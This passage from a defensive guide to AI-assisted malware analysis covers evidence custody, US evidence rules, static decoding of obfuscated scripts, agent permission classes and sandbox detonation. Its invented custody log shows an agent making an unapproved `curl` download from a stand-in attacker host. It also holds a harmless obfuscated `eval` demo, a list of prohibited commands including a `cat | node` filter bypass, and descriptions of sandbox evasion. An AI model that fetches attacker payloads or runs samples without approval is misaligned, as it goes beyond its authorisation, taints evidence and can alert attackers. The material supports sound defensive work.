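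Crosley recommends that the report pair each conclusion with the exact piece of evidence that supports it and a level of confidence. For example, a claim that an app contacts a suspicious domain deserves high confidence if the domain appears both in the app and in passive DNS observations. Crosley also recommends that the agent state what would disprove each finding and list anything it did not examine. A model's verdict that a file is malicious doesn't count as evidence in this scheme, because it is only an interpretation of the evidence.

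### How accidents damage evidence

An accident on the victim's own computer usually does more harm to the evidence than one on a disposable analysis machine, because the victim's computer may hold the only traces of the attack. The analysis machine holds only a copy of the sample, so the team can start again from the original.

Suppose Sam, one of Dana's colleagues, opened the invoice script on Monday and the malware wrote a file that restarts the malware after every reboot. If an agent runs the script on Sam's computer on Tuesday, the malware may write that file again, changing its modification time from Monday to Tuesday. The new process also changes the computer's memory, and any new files may overwrite deleted ones that an investigator could have recovered.

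Actions meant to help can also change evidence. NIST warns that turning on more logging after an incident could alter the evidence and alert the attacker, so responders should consider the effect and document what they did. An agent that runs malware by mistake might try to fix this by stopping it and deleting the files it created, but one of those files could be the only copy of the malware's second stage. The agent's instructions should therefore prohibit clean-up, and its account should not be able to delete anything from the evidence store.

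An agent's request to the C2 server can look like a victim's. If the agent and the infected computers share the office's public IP address, an investigator may not be able to tell them apart in outside records. The investigator could then count a computer as infected when it never was, or conclude that the malware remained active a day longer than it did.

The server's response may also differ from what the victim received. The attacker may have replaced the file since Monday, or the server may send different files to different visitors. A second request cannot settle this because it could return yet another file.

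### A custody log with an unauthorised request

In this invented case, Sam's computer contacted the attacker's server at 15:40 UTC on Monday. On Tuesday, an analyst called Ortiz gives an agent a copy of the script and allows only static analysis. The analysis machine should be offline, but someone connected it for an update and forgot to disconnect it.

H1 to H4 stand for full SHA-256 hashes. The complete log would also include the tool and model versions.

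| Entry | Time (UTC) | Who | Action | Hashes | Approval and network |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 09:02 | Ortiz | Exports the email from Sam's mailbox and extracts `invoice.js` | Original: H1 | Incident leader approved; mail server only |
| 2 | 09:06 | Ortiz | Stores the original read-only and makes a working copy | Copy: H1 | Approved; evidence store only |
| 3 | 09:12 | Agent | `cat invoice.js` | Input: H1 | Approved; no connection |
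| 4 | 09:20 | Agent | `python3 -I decode.py invoice.js` | Input: H1; script: H2; output: H3 | Approved; no connection |
| 5 | 09:24 | Agent | `curl -o stage2.bin https://files.invoice.example/s2` | Output: H4 | **No approval**; firewall logs one connection |
| 6 | 09:25 | Agent | `file stage2.bin` | Input: H4 | Approved; no connection |
| 7 | 09:31 | Ortiz | Stops the agent and copies the logs and `stage2.bin` to the evidence store | Copy: H4 | Incident leader approved; evidence store only |
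| 8 | 09:40 | Ortiz | Hashes the original and the working copy again | Both: H1 | Approved; evidence store only |

The agent's decoder, `decode.py`, printed the address of the second stage at 09:20. Four minutes later, the agent downloaded the second stage, which its task did not allow. It then wrote in its report that the script "downloads `stage2.bin`, a Windows program". That may describe the script accurately, but the reader cannot tell from it that the agent also downloaded the file.

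The unauthorised request affects some conclusions and leaves others intact.

| Conclusion | Does it survive? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| The agent worked on an exact copy of the exported attachment | Yes | The original and the copy both have hash H1 |
| The script contains the server's address | Yes | Anyone can run the saved decoder on the same file |
| The agent received H4 from the server on Tuesday | Yes | The command log records the file, and the firewall confirms the connection |
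| Sam's computer contacted the server on Monday | Yes, if a separate log from Monday shows it | Tuesday's request cannot prove it |
| Sam's computer received H4 | Not established | The server may have sent Sam another file |
| The attacker is unaware of the investigation | No longer safe to assume | The attacker may have seen Tuesday's request |

Ortiz could still establish what Sam's computer received by finding a copy of the second stage on its disk. If that copy also has hash H4, it is identical to the file the agent received. If Ortiz finds no copy, the report should describe H4 only as the hash of the file that the server sent to the agent on Tuesday.

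The custody log could also prevent a later misunderstanding. If the police obtain the attacker's server log, they may find two requests from the same office address. Entry 5 accounts for Tuesday's request, so nobody needs to search for a second infected computer.

The result would have been worse if the agent had run `invoice.js` at 09:24. The address from entry 4 would still be reliable, because the agent had already decoded it. But investigators would have to treat anything that appeared on the analysis machine afterwards as possibly created by the malware.

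### Authentication in US courts

Under Rule 901 of the US Federal Rules of Evidence, a party needs only enough evidence for a jury to reasonably conclude that an item is what the party claims it is. Ortiz might meet this standard by testifying about how she exported the attachment and checked its hash.

Federal Rule of Evidence 901(b)(9) allows a computer system's output to be authenticated with evidence that describes the process and shows that it produces an accurate result. According to the Texas Law Review essay *On the Potential Abrogation of Federal Rule of Evidence 901(b)(9)*, an October 2025 memo criticised this wording for confusing authenticity with reliability. The memo also warned that abolishing the rule could cause problems for simple machine-generated evidence.

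Two parts of Rule 902 let a written certificate take the place of a witness who would otherwise authenticate the item:

- Rule 902(13) covers records generated by an electronic process that produces an accurate result. A qualified person might use it to certify the firewall log.
- Rule 902(14) covers data copied from a device, storage medium or file. A qualified person certifies that the copy matches, usually by comparing hashes. Ortiz might use it for the working copy of `invoice.js`.

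The party must notify the other side in advance and let it inspect the record and the certificate. The other side can still object for reasons other than authenticity. Even a valid certificate for `invoice.js` would not show that the attacker sent the file or that the agent interpreted it correctly.

### Expert testimony and proposed Rule 707

The agent's conclusions need more support than its command log. Legal Theory Blog's *Bellin on Evidence Law's AI Problem* (2026) reproduces an article abstract in which law professor Jeffrey Bellin explains that expert witnesses must already show that their AI tools are reliable. An analyst who testifies as an expert based on an agent's work should therefore expect questions about how the agent reached its results and how they were checked.

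The rules are less clear when nobody testifies as an expert. A witness might know how to start the agent but not whether its verdicts are reliable, or a party might submit the output with only a certificate under Rule 902(13). National Law Review's *Ai Forensic Tools* (2026) says that parties offering AI output in civil cases usually need to show only relevance and authenticity.

Proposed Rule 707 would close this gap. The Advisory Committee on Evidence Rules (2026), which drafts changes to the federal rules, published a first version for comment in August 2025. This version would have applied the standards for expert testimony to "machine-generated" evidence offered without an expert. Most commenters thought the term "machine-generated" was too broad.

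The committee's revised draft covers artificial intelligence instead. It would normally require an expert to explain how the system reliably produced the evidence, but would allow other proof in exceptional circumstances. It would also require advance notice to the other side. The draft would probably cover an agent's verdict that a file is malware, but not a plain record of the agent's commands, because that record contains no expert opinion.

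Rule 707 is not in force. The committee decided in May 2026 not to recommend action on it, and Bloomberg Law's *Proposed FRE 707 Stalls* (2026) estimated that month that any version was more than three years from taking effect. In June, a higher committee sent the proposal back for more study, according to National Law Review's *Machine-Generated Evidence Challenges the Federal Rules*. Baker Botts' *Existing Rules, Emerging Changes* (2026) reports that experts at a hearing on 15 October had trouble distinguishing AI-generated conclusions from ordinary uses of software. By 3 November, officials were moving towards shelving the project on AI evidence, according to Overley's *Judiciary Stuck In AI Rulemaking Rut As Attys, Judges Protest* (2026).

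A separate proposal, Rule 901(c), concerns deepfakes, which are convincing AI fabrications. If one side produced enough evidence that an item was fabricated, the other would have to prove that it was more likely genuine than not. Mondaq's *Federal Evidence Rulemaking On AI Hits Pause* reports that the committee has not published this proposal for comment either. The rule could matter in a malware case if someone claimed that an AI system had fabricated a log, so a copy on a separate server would be useful whether or not the rule passes.

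### Weakened evidence and inadmissible evidence

In US courts, a gap in the chain of custody usually weakens an item of evidence without making it inadmissible, provided that enough evidence remains to satisfy Rule 901. The judge still lets the jury consider the item, but the jury has less reason to accept the claim it supports.

Expert testimony based on an unreliable method of analysis carries a greater risk of exclusion. Before admitting it, the judge must find that the testimony more likely than not meets the reliability requirements. The Advisory Committee on Evidence Rules reports that many courts had wrongly left this question to the jury, which contributed to a 2023 change in the rule. A judge could therefore exclude the testimony of an expert who cannot explain how an agent reached a verdict or reproduce the steps that support it.

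In Sam's case, the unauthorised request would not by itself make the original attachment inadmissible. The attachment's hash and the early log entries still support its authenticity. The downloaded file could also be admissible as the file the agent received on Tuesday, but it would be weak evidence of what ran on Sam's computer on Monday.

These distinctions follow US federal rules, and other courts may apply different ones. Brezinski and Killalea recommend asking local law enforcement to confirm that an organisation's procedures are adequate. The security team can often act on evidence too weak for a trial. For example, it can block `files.invoice.example` without proving which file Sam received.

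Ortiz should leave entry 5 in the log even though it records a mistake. Brezinski and Killalea say that evidence should be complete and that nothing about its handling should cast doubt on it. If Ortiz deleted the entry and the other side found the request in the firewall log, they could reasonably question the other seven entries.

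## Decoding an obfuscated script without running it

An agent can often recover a script's hidden text by using separate code to apply the script's transformations. Attackers commonly wrap one encoding inside another, so the agent should remove one layer at a time and read the result before choosing the next step.

### The procedure

1. Identify the format from the file's bytes, because the attacker chose the file extension. A ZIP archive normally starts with `PK`, a Windows program with `MZ`, and gzip-compressed data with the bytes `1f 8b`.
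2. List the transformations in the order the script applies them, and mark every instruction that runs text as code.
3. Decode one layer as data, using a standard decoder or a short new program.
4. Save the result as a new file, and record its size and hash.
5. Inspect the new file as text, including any addresses, file names or further encoded blocks.
6. Repeat from the first step until the text is readable or the agent reaches a stopping condition.

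The agent should check character encodings in the first step. Toda and Mori print part of a malicious Python package that gives PowerShell an encoded command beginning `cABvAHcAZQByAHMA`. This is Base64 for "powers", presumably the start of "powershell", in UTF-16, an encoding that uses two bytes for each of these letters. The second byte is always zero, which produces the repeated `A`s. An agent that reads the decoded bytes as one-byte text will find a zero after every letter and may wrongly conclude that another layer of obfuscation remains.

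### A two-layer example

The file `demo.js` below is harmless. It contains 135 bytes, with no line break at the end.

```
eval('))"iIzcvUGbw1WY4VmLv1WZk9yL6MHc0RHai0Td7kiIuQ3clRHIhBSes52bgMXagMXaoRlIoc2bs5SZs92cu92Y"(bota(lave'.split('').reverse().join(''))
```

The bytes are ordinary printable characters, and the syntax is JavaScript. The script splits the text between the single quotes into characters, reverses their order and joins them again. It then passes the result to `eval`, which runs it. The agent needs to repeat only the reversal, and can do so with this Python program, `decode1.py`:

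```
from pathlib import Path
text = Path("/samples/demo.js").read_text()
layer1 = text.split("'")[1][::-1]
Path("layer1.txt").write_text(layer1)
print(len(layer1))
```

The third line takes the 98 bytes between the first two single quotes and reverses them. The input to the reversal is:

```
))"iIzcvUGbw1WY4VmLv1WZk9yL6MHc0RHai0Td7kiIuQ3clRHIhBSes52bgMXagMXaoRlIoc2bs5SZs92cu92Y"(bota(lave
```

The output, also 98 bytes, goes into `layer1.txt`:

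```
eval(atob("Y29uc29sZS5sb2coIlRoaXMgaXMgb25seSBhIHRlc3QuIik7dT0iaHR0cHM6Ly9kZW1vLmV4YW1wbGUvczIi"))
```

The agent hashes this file and reads it. The function `atob` decodes Base64, and a second `eval` would run the decoded text. The 84 bytes between the double quotes are the next input:

```
Y29uc29sZS5sb2coIlRoaXMgaXMgb25seSBhIHRlc3QuIik7dT0iaHR0cHM6Ly9kZW1vLmV4YW1wbGUvczIi
```

A second program, `decode2.py`, handles this layer:

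```
import base64
from pathlib import Path
text = Path("layer1.txt").read_text()
layer2 = base64.b64decode(text.split('"')[1], validate=True)
Path("layer2.txt").write_bytes(layer2)
print(len(layer2))
```

The result has 63 bytes:

```
console.log("This is only a test.");u="https://demo.example/s2"
```

Running this text would print one sentence and store an address in a variable without contacting it. No encoded text remains, so the decoding is finished. The agent can report the address as an indicator but should not request it.

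The byte counts help catch mistakes. Reversing text doesn't change its length, and Base64 turns every three bytes into four characters, so 84 characters without padding must give 63 bytes. A different number would suggest the agent had copied the block incorrectly. The `validate=True` setting makes Python report characters that don't belong in Base64, which it would otherwise skip.

### Stopping conditions

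An agent should stop decoding when it meets a transformation it cannot identify. Base64 decoders accept many strings that were never Base64 and return meaningless bytes, so decoding without an error does not prove that the string was Base64. Toda and Mori mention agents that get stuck trying to decode random strings this way. The operator can set a limit, such as five attempts on one layer, and tell the agent to report what it tried.

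The agent should also stop when decoding needs a value that exists only at run time. For example, a script may use the victim's computer name as its decryption key. The security team may know that name and can give it to the agent as data, so running the script isn't always necessary.

The third reason to stop is that the next step requires network access. In the `ethereim` package, the decrypted code only fetches the next stage, so the agent has nothing more to decode. It should report the address and leave any download to the person who can approve contacting it.

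### Why a print statement is not enough

In the example, `atob` returns text and `eval` runs it. Replacing the outer `eval` with `console.log` and running `demo.js` would print the first layer safely, but only because this file contains nothing else. Consider a script with two encoded blocks, `a` and `b`:

`var r=eval; eval(a); r(b);`

The first instruction gives `eval` a second name, so if the agent replaces `eval(` with `console.log(`, the script prints `a` and then runs `b`. Toda and Mori found a real package that similarly gave Python's `exec` another name and hid the calls inside chains of small functions.

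Replacing the `eval` function itself before the script starts would also catch calls made through the second name. It would not catch `ethter`, another package that Toda and Mori describe, because `ethter` writes its decoded code to a new Python file and runs that file as a separate process with its own unmodified functions. `decode1.py` avoids both problems because it never passes any part of the sample to a JavaScript interpreter.

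### Letting the model decode the text itself

A model can also try to work out the hidden text by reading the script. This runs no code, but models make many errors when a value takes several steps to decode. *SCRIPTIOC-BENCH* (Kim, Cui and colleagues, 2026) tested ten models on 634 malicious scripts, asking each to find indicators such as addresses and file names without running anything. GPT-5.6 Terra found 91.7% of the indicators that appeared in plain text, 69.9% of those that needed two standard decoding steps, and 19.0% of those that needed three or more. The last group contained only 21 indicators, so that figure is uncertain, but the other models also did much worse as the number of steps grew.

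Some wrong answers look convincing. Smaller models often copied example addresses from their instructions when they could not decode the real ones, so an operator should avoid putting realistic addresses in a prompt. *CASCADE* (Jiang, Kovuri and colleagues, 2025) describes a test in which Gemini 2.5 Pro was asked to decode a program that prints "world hello". The model's reasoning contained the right phrase, but it answered "hello world", probably because that order is much more common in its training data, a bias that a short decoder doesn't have.

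However, access to decoding tools does not guarantee good results. Kim and colleagues gave a small model, Qwen3-8B, functions for Base64, reversal, XOR and similar operations. With these tools, the model found more plain-text indicators than without them, but fewer of those that needed standard decoding, partly because the extra tool calls led to more unusable answers. The researchers did not repeat the test with a stronger model or let any model write its own decoder.

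### Running the decoder safely

The agent's decoder should be harmless, but the agent may have written it badly or copied a dangerous line from the sample. The decoder should therefore run with as little access as possible.

The agent works in a new, empty directory, away from the sample. On Linux, it can run:

`timeout -k 2 10 prlimit --fsize=1000000 --as=500000000 python3 -I decode1.py | head -c 4000`

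- `timeout` asks the program to stop after ten seconds and forces it to stop two seconds later.
- `--fsize` limits each file the program writes to one million bytes, and `--as` limits its memory to about 500 MB.
- `-I` starts Python in isolated mode.
- `head` limits the printed output to 4,000 bytes.

The file and memory limits matter because a small compressed block can expand to many gigabytes. The command doesn't disconnect the network, so it should run on the offline analysis machine or in a container started with `--network none`.

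According to *Using AI Agents to Analyze Malware on REMnux*, the REMnux server gives the agent a summary when tool output exceeds about 32 KB, and saves the full text in files. The summary may leave out the line that contains the next encoded block, so the agent should save each layer to a file and read it in sections.

### Parsing, constant evaluation, emulation and partial execution

Decoding `demo.js` takes only two simple operations. Other scripts spread a value across dozens of variables or build it in a loop, and the agent may need a more powerful method to decode them.

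| Method | What it can recover | What it may run |
|---|---|---|
| Parsing | The script's structure, function names and plain strings | None of the sample's code |
| Constant evaluation | Values that depend only on constants in the script, such as joined strings and arithmetic | None of the sample's code, because the analysis tool does the calculation |
| Emulation | Values built in loops, and actions the script would attempt | The sample's instructions, with an imitation of the operating system |
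| Partial execution | The results of selected functions | Those functions, in a real interpreter |

The first two methods are static analysis, but the other two run some of the sample's code, so they must be authorised as part of the task. An emulator may record a download attempt without connecting to the server, but some can contact real servers, which is another reason to keep the machine offline.

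The methods work well in sequence. *From Obfuscated to Obvious* (Zhou, Ying and colleagues, 2025) describes JSimplifier, a tool for JavaScript that first parses the script and calculates whatever it can from constants. It leaves some expressions alone, such as a check for a web browser, because the result depends on where the script runs. It then runs selected fragments in a separate context in Node.js, a program that runs JavaScript outside a browser. The context has no access to files or the network, and the tool limits running time, memory and recursion (functions calling themselves). Zhou and colleagues still recommend additional isolation for regular use, which is sensible because this Node.js feature was not designed to contain hostile code.

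Google's CASCADE runs even less of the script. It targets Obfuscator.IO, a program that moves a script's strings into a shuffled table and replaces each one with a function call such as `getString(438)`. CASCADE recovers the strings in four steps:

1. Gemini identifies the three functions that store, shuffle and fetch the strings.
2. A conventional program checks that these functions depend on each other in the expected way and on nothing else in the script.
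3. A JavaScript engine loads only those functions and calls `getString` with the required numbers.
4. Constant evaluation puts the returned strings back into the script and works out any expressions that use them.

CASCADE succeeded on 98.93% of 11,736 test files, averaging about 2.3 seconds per file. The files were ordinary scripts that Jiang and colleagues had obfuscated, so the success rate on malware may differ. The check in the second step doesn't prove that the functions are harmless. An attacker could imitate the usual pattern and add another command to one of them, so the engine still needs a sandbox.

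A tool's description may not make clear whether it runs the script. *AI-Generated PowerShell Malware* (2026) describes PowerDecode as a deobfuscation tool, but PowerDecode works by running the script in a sandbox. An agent allowed to "deobfuscate" a file could choose PowerDecode without realising that this would run the sample. Running a script also doesn't always decode it fully. The researchers dropped 13 scripts that were still obfuscated after PowerDecode and manual work.

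### Three permission classes

The operator can turn these distinctions into rules that a program enforces before each tool call. The program runs automatic calls without approval, holds calls that require approval until a person approves them, and blocks prohibited calls even if the agent gives a good reason.

*A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) recommends checking first whether an action is prohibited, then whether it is automatically permitted, and sending everything else to a person. It sorts actions by how much damage they could do and whether someone could undo them. Creating a text file on a disposable machine is easy to undo, but an analyst can't erase a request from an attacker's server log.

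The table shows this approach applied to static analysis on REMnux. The tool names come from *Using AI Agents to Analyze Malware on REMnux* and Portland State University's *AI-Assisted Security Analysis*.

| Class | Tool calls |
|---|---|
| Automatic | `get_file_info`, `list_files`, `suggest_tools` and `get_tool_help` |
| Automatic | `extract_iocs` on decoded text, and `extract_archive` into the case folder with a size limit |
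| Automatic | A dedicated Base64, reversal or XOR tool that accepts text and returns text |
| Approval required | `run_tool` with a new decoder, such as `python3 -I decode1.py` |
| Approval required | `analyze_file`, until the operator has checked which programs it runs for that file type |
| Approval required | Any emulator or partial execution |
| Approval required | `upload_from_host`, which copies a file from the host |
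| Prohibited | `node demo.js`, or any other command that runs the whole sample |
| Prohibited | `eval`, `exec` or `Invoke-Expression` on decoded text |
| Prohibited | `curl`, `dig` or a browser visit to an address from the sample |
| Prohibited | Changes to the original sample, the logs or the agent's own permission settings |

The last prohibition prevents an agent from giving itself more access. *PegasusAI Studio* (2026) describes a scientific computing system with a similar rule. Its agents can edit project files freely but must ask before writing elsewhere in the user's home folder, because their permission settings might be stored there. For malware analysis, a complete ban is better, since the agent doesn't need to change these settings.

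Prohibited here means prohibited during static analysis. If someone later authorises detonation, that work should have its own environment and rules.

### Narrow tools and the general shell

A narrow tool performs one operation on limited input. Toda and Mori's system has one tool that decodes Base64 and another that decrypts Fernet, an encryption format they found in about 40% of malicious packages. The operator can allow both automatically because neither runs its input as a command. Another tool, for encodings the narrow tools cannot handle, runs any Python code in a sandbox, so it needs stricter rules.

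`run_tool` on REMnux is harder to classify. Printing a script and running it are both `run_tool` calls, so a rule based on the tool's name cannot separate them. A filter could inspect the command instead, but it would have to recognise every way to run a file. Suppose it allows commands that begin with `cat` and blocks those that begin with `node`. The agent could still run the sample with:

`cat demo.js | node`

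REMnux supports joining commands like this. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) found the same weakness in ordinary programming work, based on 290 public reports of coding agents misusing files. In 77, the agent could use the shell to avoid restrictions on its other tools, and in 52, a filter checked a command's wording but missed its effect. People submit such reports when something has gone wrong, so these numbers don't show how often filters fail overall.

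The best arrangement is to provide narrow tools for common work and require approval for every `run_tool` call. If analysts keep approving the same decoder, the operator can turn it into a narrow tool. Filters still help catch obvious mistakes.

### What the reviewer must see

A person can approve a command safely only if they know what it will do. A reviewer can't tell from `python3 -I decode1.py` alone whether it is safe, because its effect depends on what `decode1.py` contains. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), most approval requests in current products show just the raw command on one line, which gives the reviewer very little information.

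For the first decoder in the example, the request should contain:

| Item | What the reviewer sees |
|---|---|
| Exact command | The full command, including its limits |
| Working directory and account | The empty case directory and an account without administrator rights |
| Code | All five lines of `decode1.py`, with the file's hash |
| Input | `/samples/demo.js`, 135 bytes, with its hash |
| Expected output | `layer1.txt` in the case directory |
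| Network | None |
| Agent's explanation | "Reverses the quoted text", clearly labelled as the agent's own words |

The reviewer should look for any line that passes text from the sample to an interpreter, starts another program or opens a network connection. A request that involves emulation or partial execution should also name the functions that will run.

*Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) recommends that separate, trusted software produce this display from the actual tool call, and that the system run only the call the reviewer approved. Recording the decoder's hash lets the system detect whether the agent has changed `decode1.py` since approval and, if so, ask for approval again.

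An analyst who gets too many approval requests is unlikely to review them carefully. In the AutoIt analysis on REMnux, asking about every call would have interrupted the analyst roughly every 16 seconds. In *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a survey of software developers, only 47.7% of respondents believed they read permission requests carefully. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026), another developer survey, found that even among developers who carefully reviewed most or all of an agent's code, 61% often approved at least one type of action without a close look.

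*Let the Agent Do It?* also cites a report that Claude Code users approve 93% of requests. Most of those requests may have been harmless, so the rate alone doesn't show carelessness, but a reviewer who almost always answers yes can easily miss the rare dangerous one. Allowing harmless calls automatically therefore makes the remaining approvals safer as well as faster.

One approval per new decoder is a reasonable compromise. The same approval can cover 50 similar scripts, provided that the decoder's hash is unchanged and it treats every input as data. Approving a whole plan at once would also reduce interruptions, but a plan cannot cover layers that nobody has decoded yet.

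### Lost information and slower work

Analysts may object that these limits make the agent less useful. Running a script in a sandbox can reveal the address of the server it contacts in seconds, while decoding several layers of obfuscation may take much longer. Some information also exists only while the script runs.

Static analysis can recover more than the agent's first attempt suggests. In Kim and colleagues' test, 1,230 of the 2,580 indicators depended on logic specific to one script, and the best model found only 46.1% of those. Two human experts had established all 2,580 by static analysis, so most of what the models missed could be found without running the script, although finding it took skilled work. The test excluded values that depended on outside information, so it cannot show how often static analysis reaches a dead end.

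Running the script can also miss information. Many of the older scripts in the test contained a list of servers and tried each one until a download worked. If the first server works, the run may never reveal the others, but decoding the list shows all of them.

The delay depends mainly on how familiar the encoding is. CASCADE decodes scripts from one common obfuscator in seconds, and an approved decoder can process a whole campaign without further approval. An unfamiliar encoding may take an analyst hours. In an emergency, that may be too long, and the person leading the response may reasonably choose to detonate the script sooner. The agent should not make that choice just because decoding has become difficult.

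### When to move to detonation

A case should move to detonation when static decoding has reached a stopping condition and the missing information would change what the team does. For example, the agent may have decoded enough of a script to see that it creates a password-stealing program whose name depends on Windows settings. If the team needs that name to search for other infected computers, running the script on a prepared Windows machine may be the best way to get it.

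If the team only needs to decide whether to block the attachment, the decoded script is enough evidence. Running it would add risk without changing the decision.

Detonation also won't solve every decoding problem. If the next layer is on the attacker's server, running the script offline will show the request but not the file. The team needs approval to contact the server, whether the team downloads the file directly or lets the script download it.

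Before handing the case to an analyst, the agent should save every layer it decoded, along with the decoder that produced it, and state exactly where it stopped. It should also write down what the analyst needs to learn by running the script, such as the name the script gives the new program. The analyst can then choose a machine with the right settings and decide in advance what to record.

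## Running a sample deliberately under containment

*pokiSEC* (2025), which describes a disposable malware sandbox, lists behaviours that running a sample can expose, including new processes, changes to Windows settings, dropped files and outgoing connections. The analyst should start with a specific question, because "What does this file do?" is too broad for the analyst to tell when a run has answered it.

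Ortiz might ask which file the invoice malware uses to restart after a reboot on a computer set up like Sam's. She could also ask which servers the sample tries to reach, or whether the company's security software detects it. Searching for the sample's hash may turn up an existing sandbox report with the answers, making a new run unnecessary.

### Authorising the run

The incident leader should authorise any run that belongs to an active investigation. Services that process malware in bulk can't ask a person to approve every file. *Malware Dynamic Analysis Evasion Techniques* (2018) cites a McAfee figure of more than 600,000 new samples a day. For bulk processing, the laboratory's owner can give standing permission for offline runs with a fixed set-up and time limit. The agent can propose a run but should never approve one.

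The approval should identify the sample by its hash and state the question the run is meant to answer, the snapshot to use, the network setting and the time limit. Changing any of these requires a new approval. For example, permission to run the sample for ten minutes with simulated services does not cover a second run with an internet connection, even if the first run showed nothing.

### From clean snapshot to disposal

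The virtual machine that runs the sample is called the guest. A run has six steps:

1. Restore the guest's clean snapshot. Clear the logs of the previous run, after copying them to the evidence store.
2. Test the isolation from inside the guest, then turn on any simulated services.
3. Start recording outside the guest, at least on the gateway that carries its network traffic.
4. Copy in the sample, check its hash, and start the sample and the timer together.
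5. When the time is up, save a snapshot that includes the guest's memory, then collect the results.
6. Delete the guest or return it to the clean snapshot, even if the sample appeared to do nothing.

Recording is best done from outside the guest because malware can stop or alter programs running beside it. *An Orchestrated Sandbox for Side-Channel Analysis of Cyber-Physical Systems Malware* (Udeshi, Putrevu et al., 2025) describes a Linux sandbox that records network traffic, disk activity and processor activity from the host. But it has to record system calls (a program's requests to the operating system) from inside the guest. One sample, Kinsing, disables monitoring services such as SSH, so the sandbox turns SSH back on after the run.

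A longer time limit can reveal more of a sample's behavior, but it uses more machine time. *A Large Language Model Approach to Generating Bypass Rules for Malware Evasion*, published in May 2026, allowed each run up to 200 seconds. When Udeshi and colleagues ran Kinsing with internet access, it downloaded its main payload about 270 seconds into the recording, so a 200-second run would have missed it. But a team with 200 samples a day would need about 33 hours of machine time to run each for ten minutes, compared with 11 hours at 200 seconds. It makes sense to start with short runs, then rerun important samples for longer if they show little.

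### Separating the agent from the guest

The agent that plans a run should not have a command line on the guest or control of the virtual machine software. It can write a plan with the details from the approval, and a fixed program called a controller can check the plan against the approval and run it only if the two match. If prompt injection hijacks the agent, the controller will still reject an unapproved network setting.

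The May 2026 study divided the work in a similar way. Its language models wrote rules for the sandbox, while a separate controller submitted the samples, retrieved the results and restored snapshots. The Windows guest ran inside another virtual machine, so the malware would have had to escape both.

The controller needs protection too. In the 2014 training laboratory that Palkmets and colleagues describe, the gateway starts and stops the guest over a passwordless connection to the host, so malware that took over the gateway could control the host's virtual machines. A laboratory for real samples should require authentication on this connection.

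Results should return to the agent as files. These files can contain prompt injection, so the agent that reads them should not be able to start another run without approval.

### Simulated internet services

Malware often contacts a server before doing anything else, and may stop if nothing replies. *Counterfeiting The Pipes With FakeNet 2.0* (Sikorski, 2014) gives this as a reason to simulate a network, since malware that runs for longer reveals more indicators. INetSim and FakeNet-NG imitate common internet services. According to Debian, INetSim covers web, email, DNS, file transfer, chat and time services. According to its developers at FLARE, a team at the security company FireEye, FakeNet-NG can run on the guest or on a separate machine. A separate machine is safer because the malware can't easily interfere with it.

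Suppose the invoice script requests `http://files.invoice.example/s2` in a laboratory with INetSim on the gateway:

1. The script asks DNS for the address of `files.invoice.example`. The gateway redirects the question to INetSim, which answers with its own address, such as `10.0.0.1`.
2. The script connects to `10.0.0.1` and requests `/s2`. INetSim records the request and returns a standard web page.

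Ortiz learns the domain, the path and the details the script sent with its request, and the attacker's server receives nothing. A sample that contacts an IP address directly skips the domain lookup, so the gateway must redirect that traffic as well.

FakeNet-NG can also match its reply to the request. If malware requests a file ending in `.exe`, FakeNet-NG sends a harmless Windows program that displays a message box, according to *FakeNet Genie* (Haigh, 2020). If the message appears, the analyst knows the malware runs what it downloads.

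Encrypted requests need more preparation. FakeNet-NG can decrypt them by intercepting traffic between the malware and the simulated website, but its default settings did not do this for ordinary HTTPS traffic when Haigh wrote. Decryption can also fail because some malware rejects the simulator's certificate and disconnects.

INetSim can report a false date to malware that waits for a particular day, as Help Net Security's *Analyze the network behavior of unknown malware samples* explains. If the malware reads the guest's clock rather than getting the date from the network, the operator has to change that clock instead.

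### When the malware needs a valid reply

A standard reply is useless if the malware checks its contents. For example, Haigh says the malware may require an image that contains a hidden script, a program that ends with a particular hash, or a message encrypted with a value from the malware's request. Analysts can configure FakeNet-NG to send such replies, but they first have to learn the required format, usually through static analysis.

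A language model can do some of this work. In *LLM-assisted Generation of Pseudo-C2 Servers for IoT Malware Dynamic Analysis*, Hasui, Matsugaya and colleagues (2026) used Claude to write a replacement command server for Mirai. Mirai infects devices such as cameras and routers, then waits for commands to flood a target with traffic. Claude examined the compiled malware through a reverse-engineering tool, described how it communicates, and wrote a Python server from that description.

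The researchers tested the server on a closed network of three virtual machines, which held the malware, the server and a target. Before continuing, the malware checks whether one of Google's DNS servers responds, so the researchers redirected that check and answered it locally. The server fully reproduced seven of Mirai's ten attack types. Two others produced no attack traffic because the network had no DNS or web server for them to use, and one made only connection attempts.

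Mirai's source code has been public since 2016, so Claude might have remembered the answers. Hasui and colleagues therefore repeated the test after changing the server address, encryption key and command numbers. Claude found all the new values, although it needed an extra tool to read one. This shows that it read the values from the program. However, the altered version kept Mirai's structure, so familiarity with the public code may still have helped. The researchers did not test other malware families, and they observed each attack for only ten seconds.

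A replacement server like this sends real attack commands. An operator should use it only on a closed network, and someone should review the code before running it.

### Malware that detects the sandbox

The methods that malware uses to avoid revealing itself in a sandbox fall into a few broad groups:

- Environment checks look for differences between the guest and an ordinary computer, such as missing hardware or too few user accounts.
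- Activity checks look for signs of a person using the mouse or keyboard.
- Timing checks measure whether operations take unusually long, which can happen when an analysis tool is watching.
- Delayed execution postpones the harmful behaviour until after a typical sandbox run has ended.

Malware can also stay inactive for reasons unrelated to a sandbox. StealC, a password stealer described in the May 2026 study, checks the computer's language to avoid certain countries. It also exits after a fixed date, when its criminal customer's licence expires, so an old sample may do nothing even on a real computer.

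A file that shows no malicious behavior when run may still be harmful. The report should state how long the sample ran, which network setting the operator used and whether the program exited early. Static analysis can then help find the condition that stopped it. Palkmets and colleagues recommend designing the laboratory so that advanced malware that will not run in a virtual machine can be run on a physical one instead.

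### The May 2026 study of model-written rules

The study tested whether language models could help a sandbox get past these checks. Its system, ABLE, uses CAPE, a sandbox that can intervene while a program runs. An analyst writes a rule that pairs a byte pattern with an action, such as skipping an instruction. When the program reaches matching code, CAPE carries out the action. Writing these rules by hand requires detailed knowledge of each sample.

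The researchers selected 334 Windows samples from MalwareBazaar, a public malware collection, that existing tools had marked as evasive. They ran each sample at least four times without rules and kept the run that triggered the most behavioural signatures, CAPE's labels for suspicious actions. A model then read a record of the instructions leading to the sample's exit and wrote a rule. If the rule failed, the model received information about the failure and could revise the rule twice.

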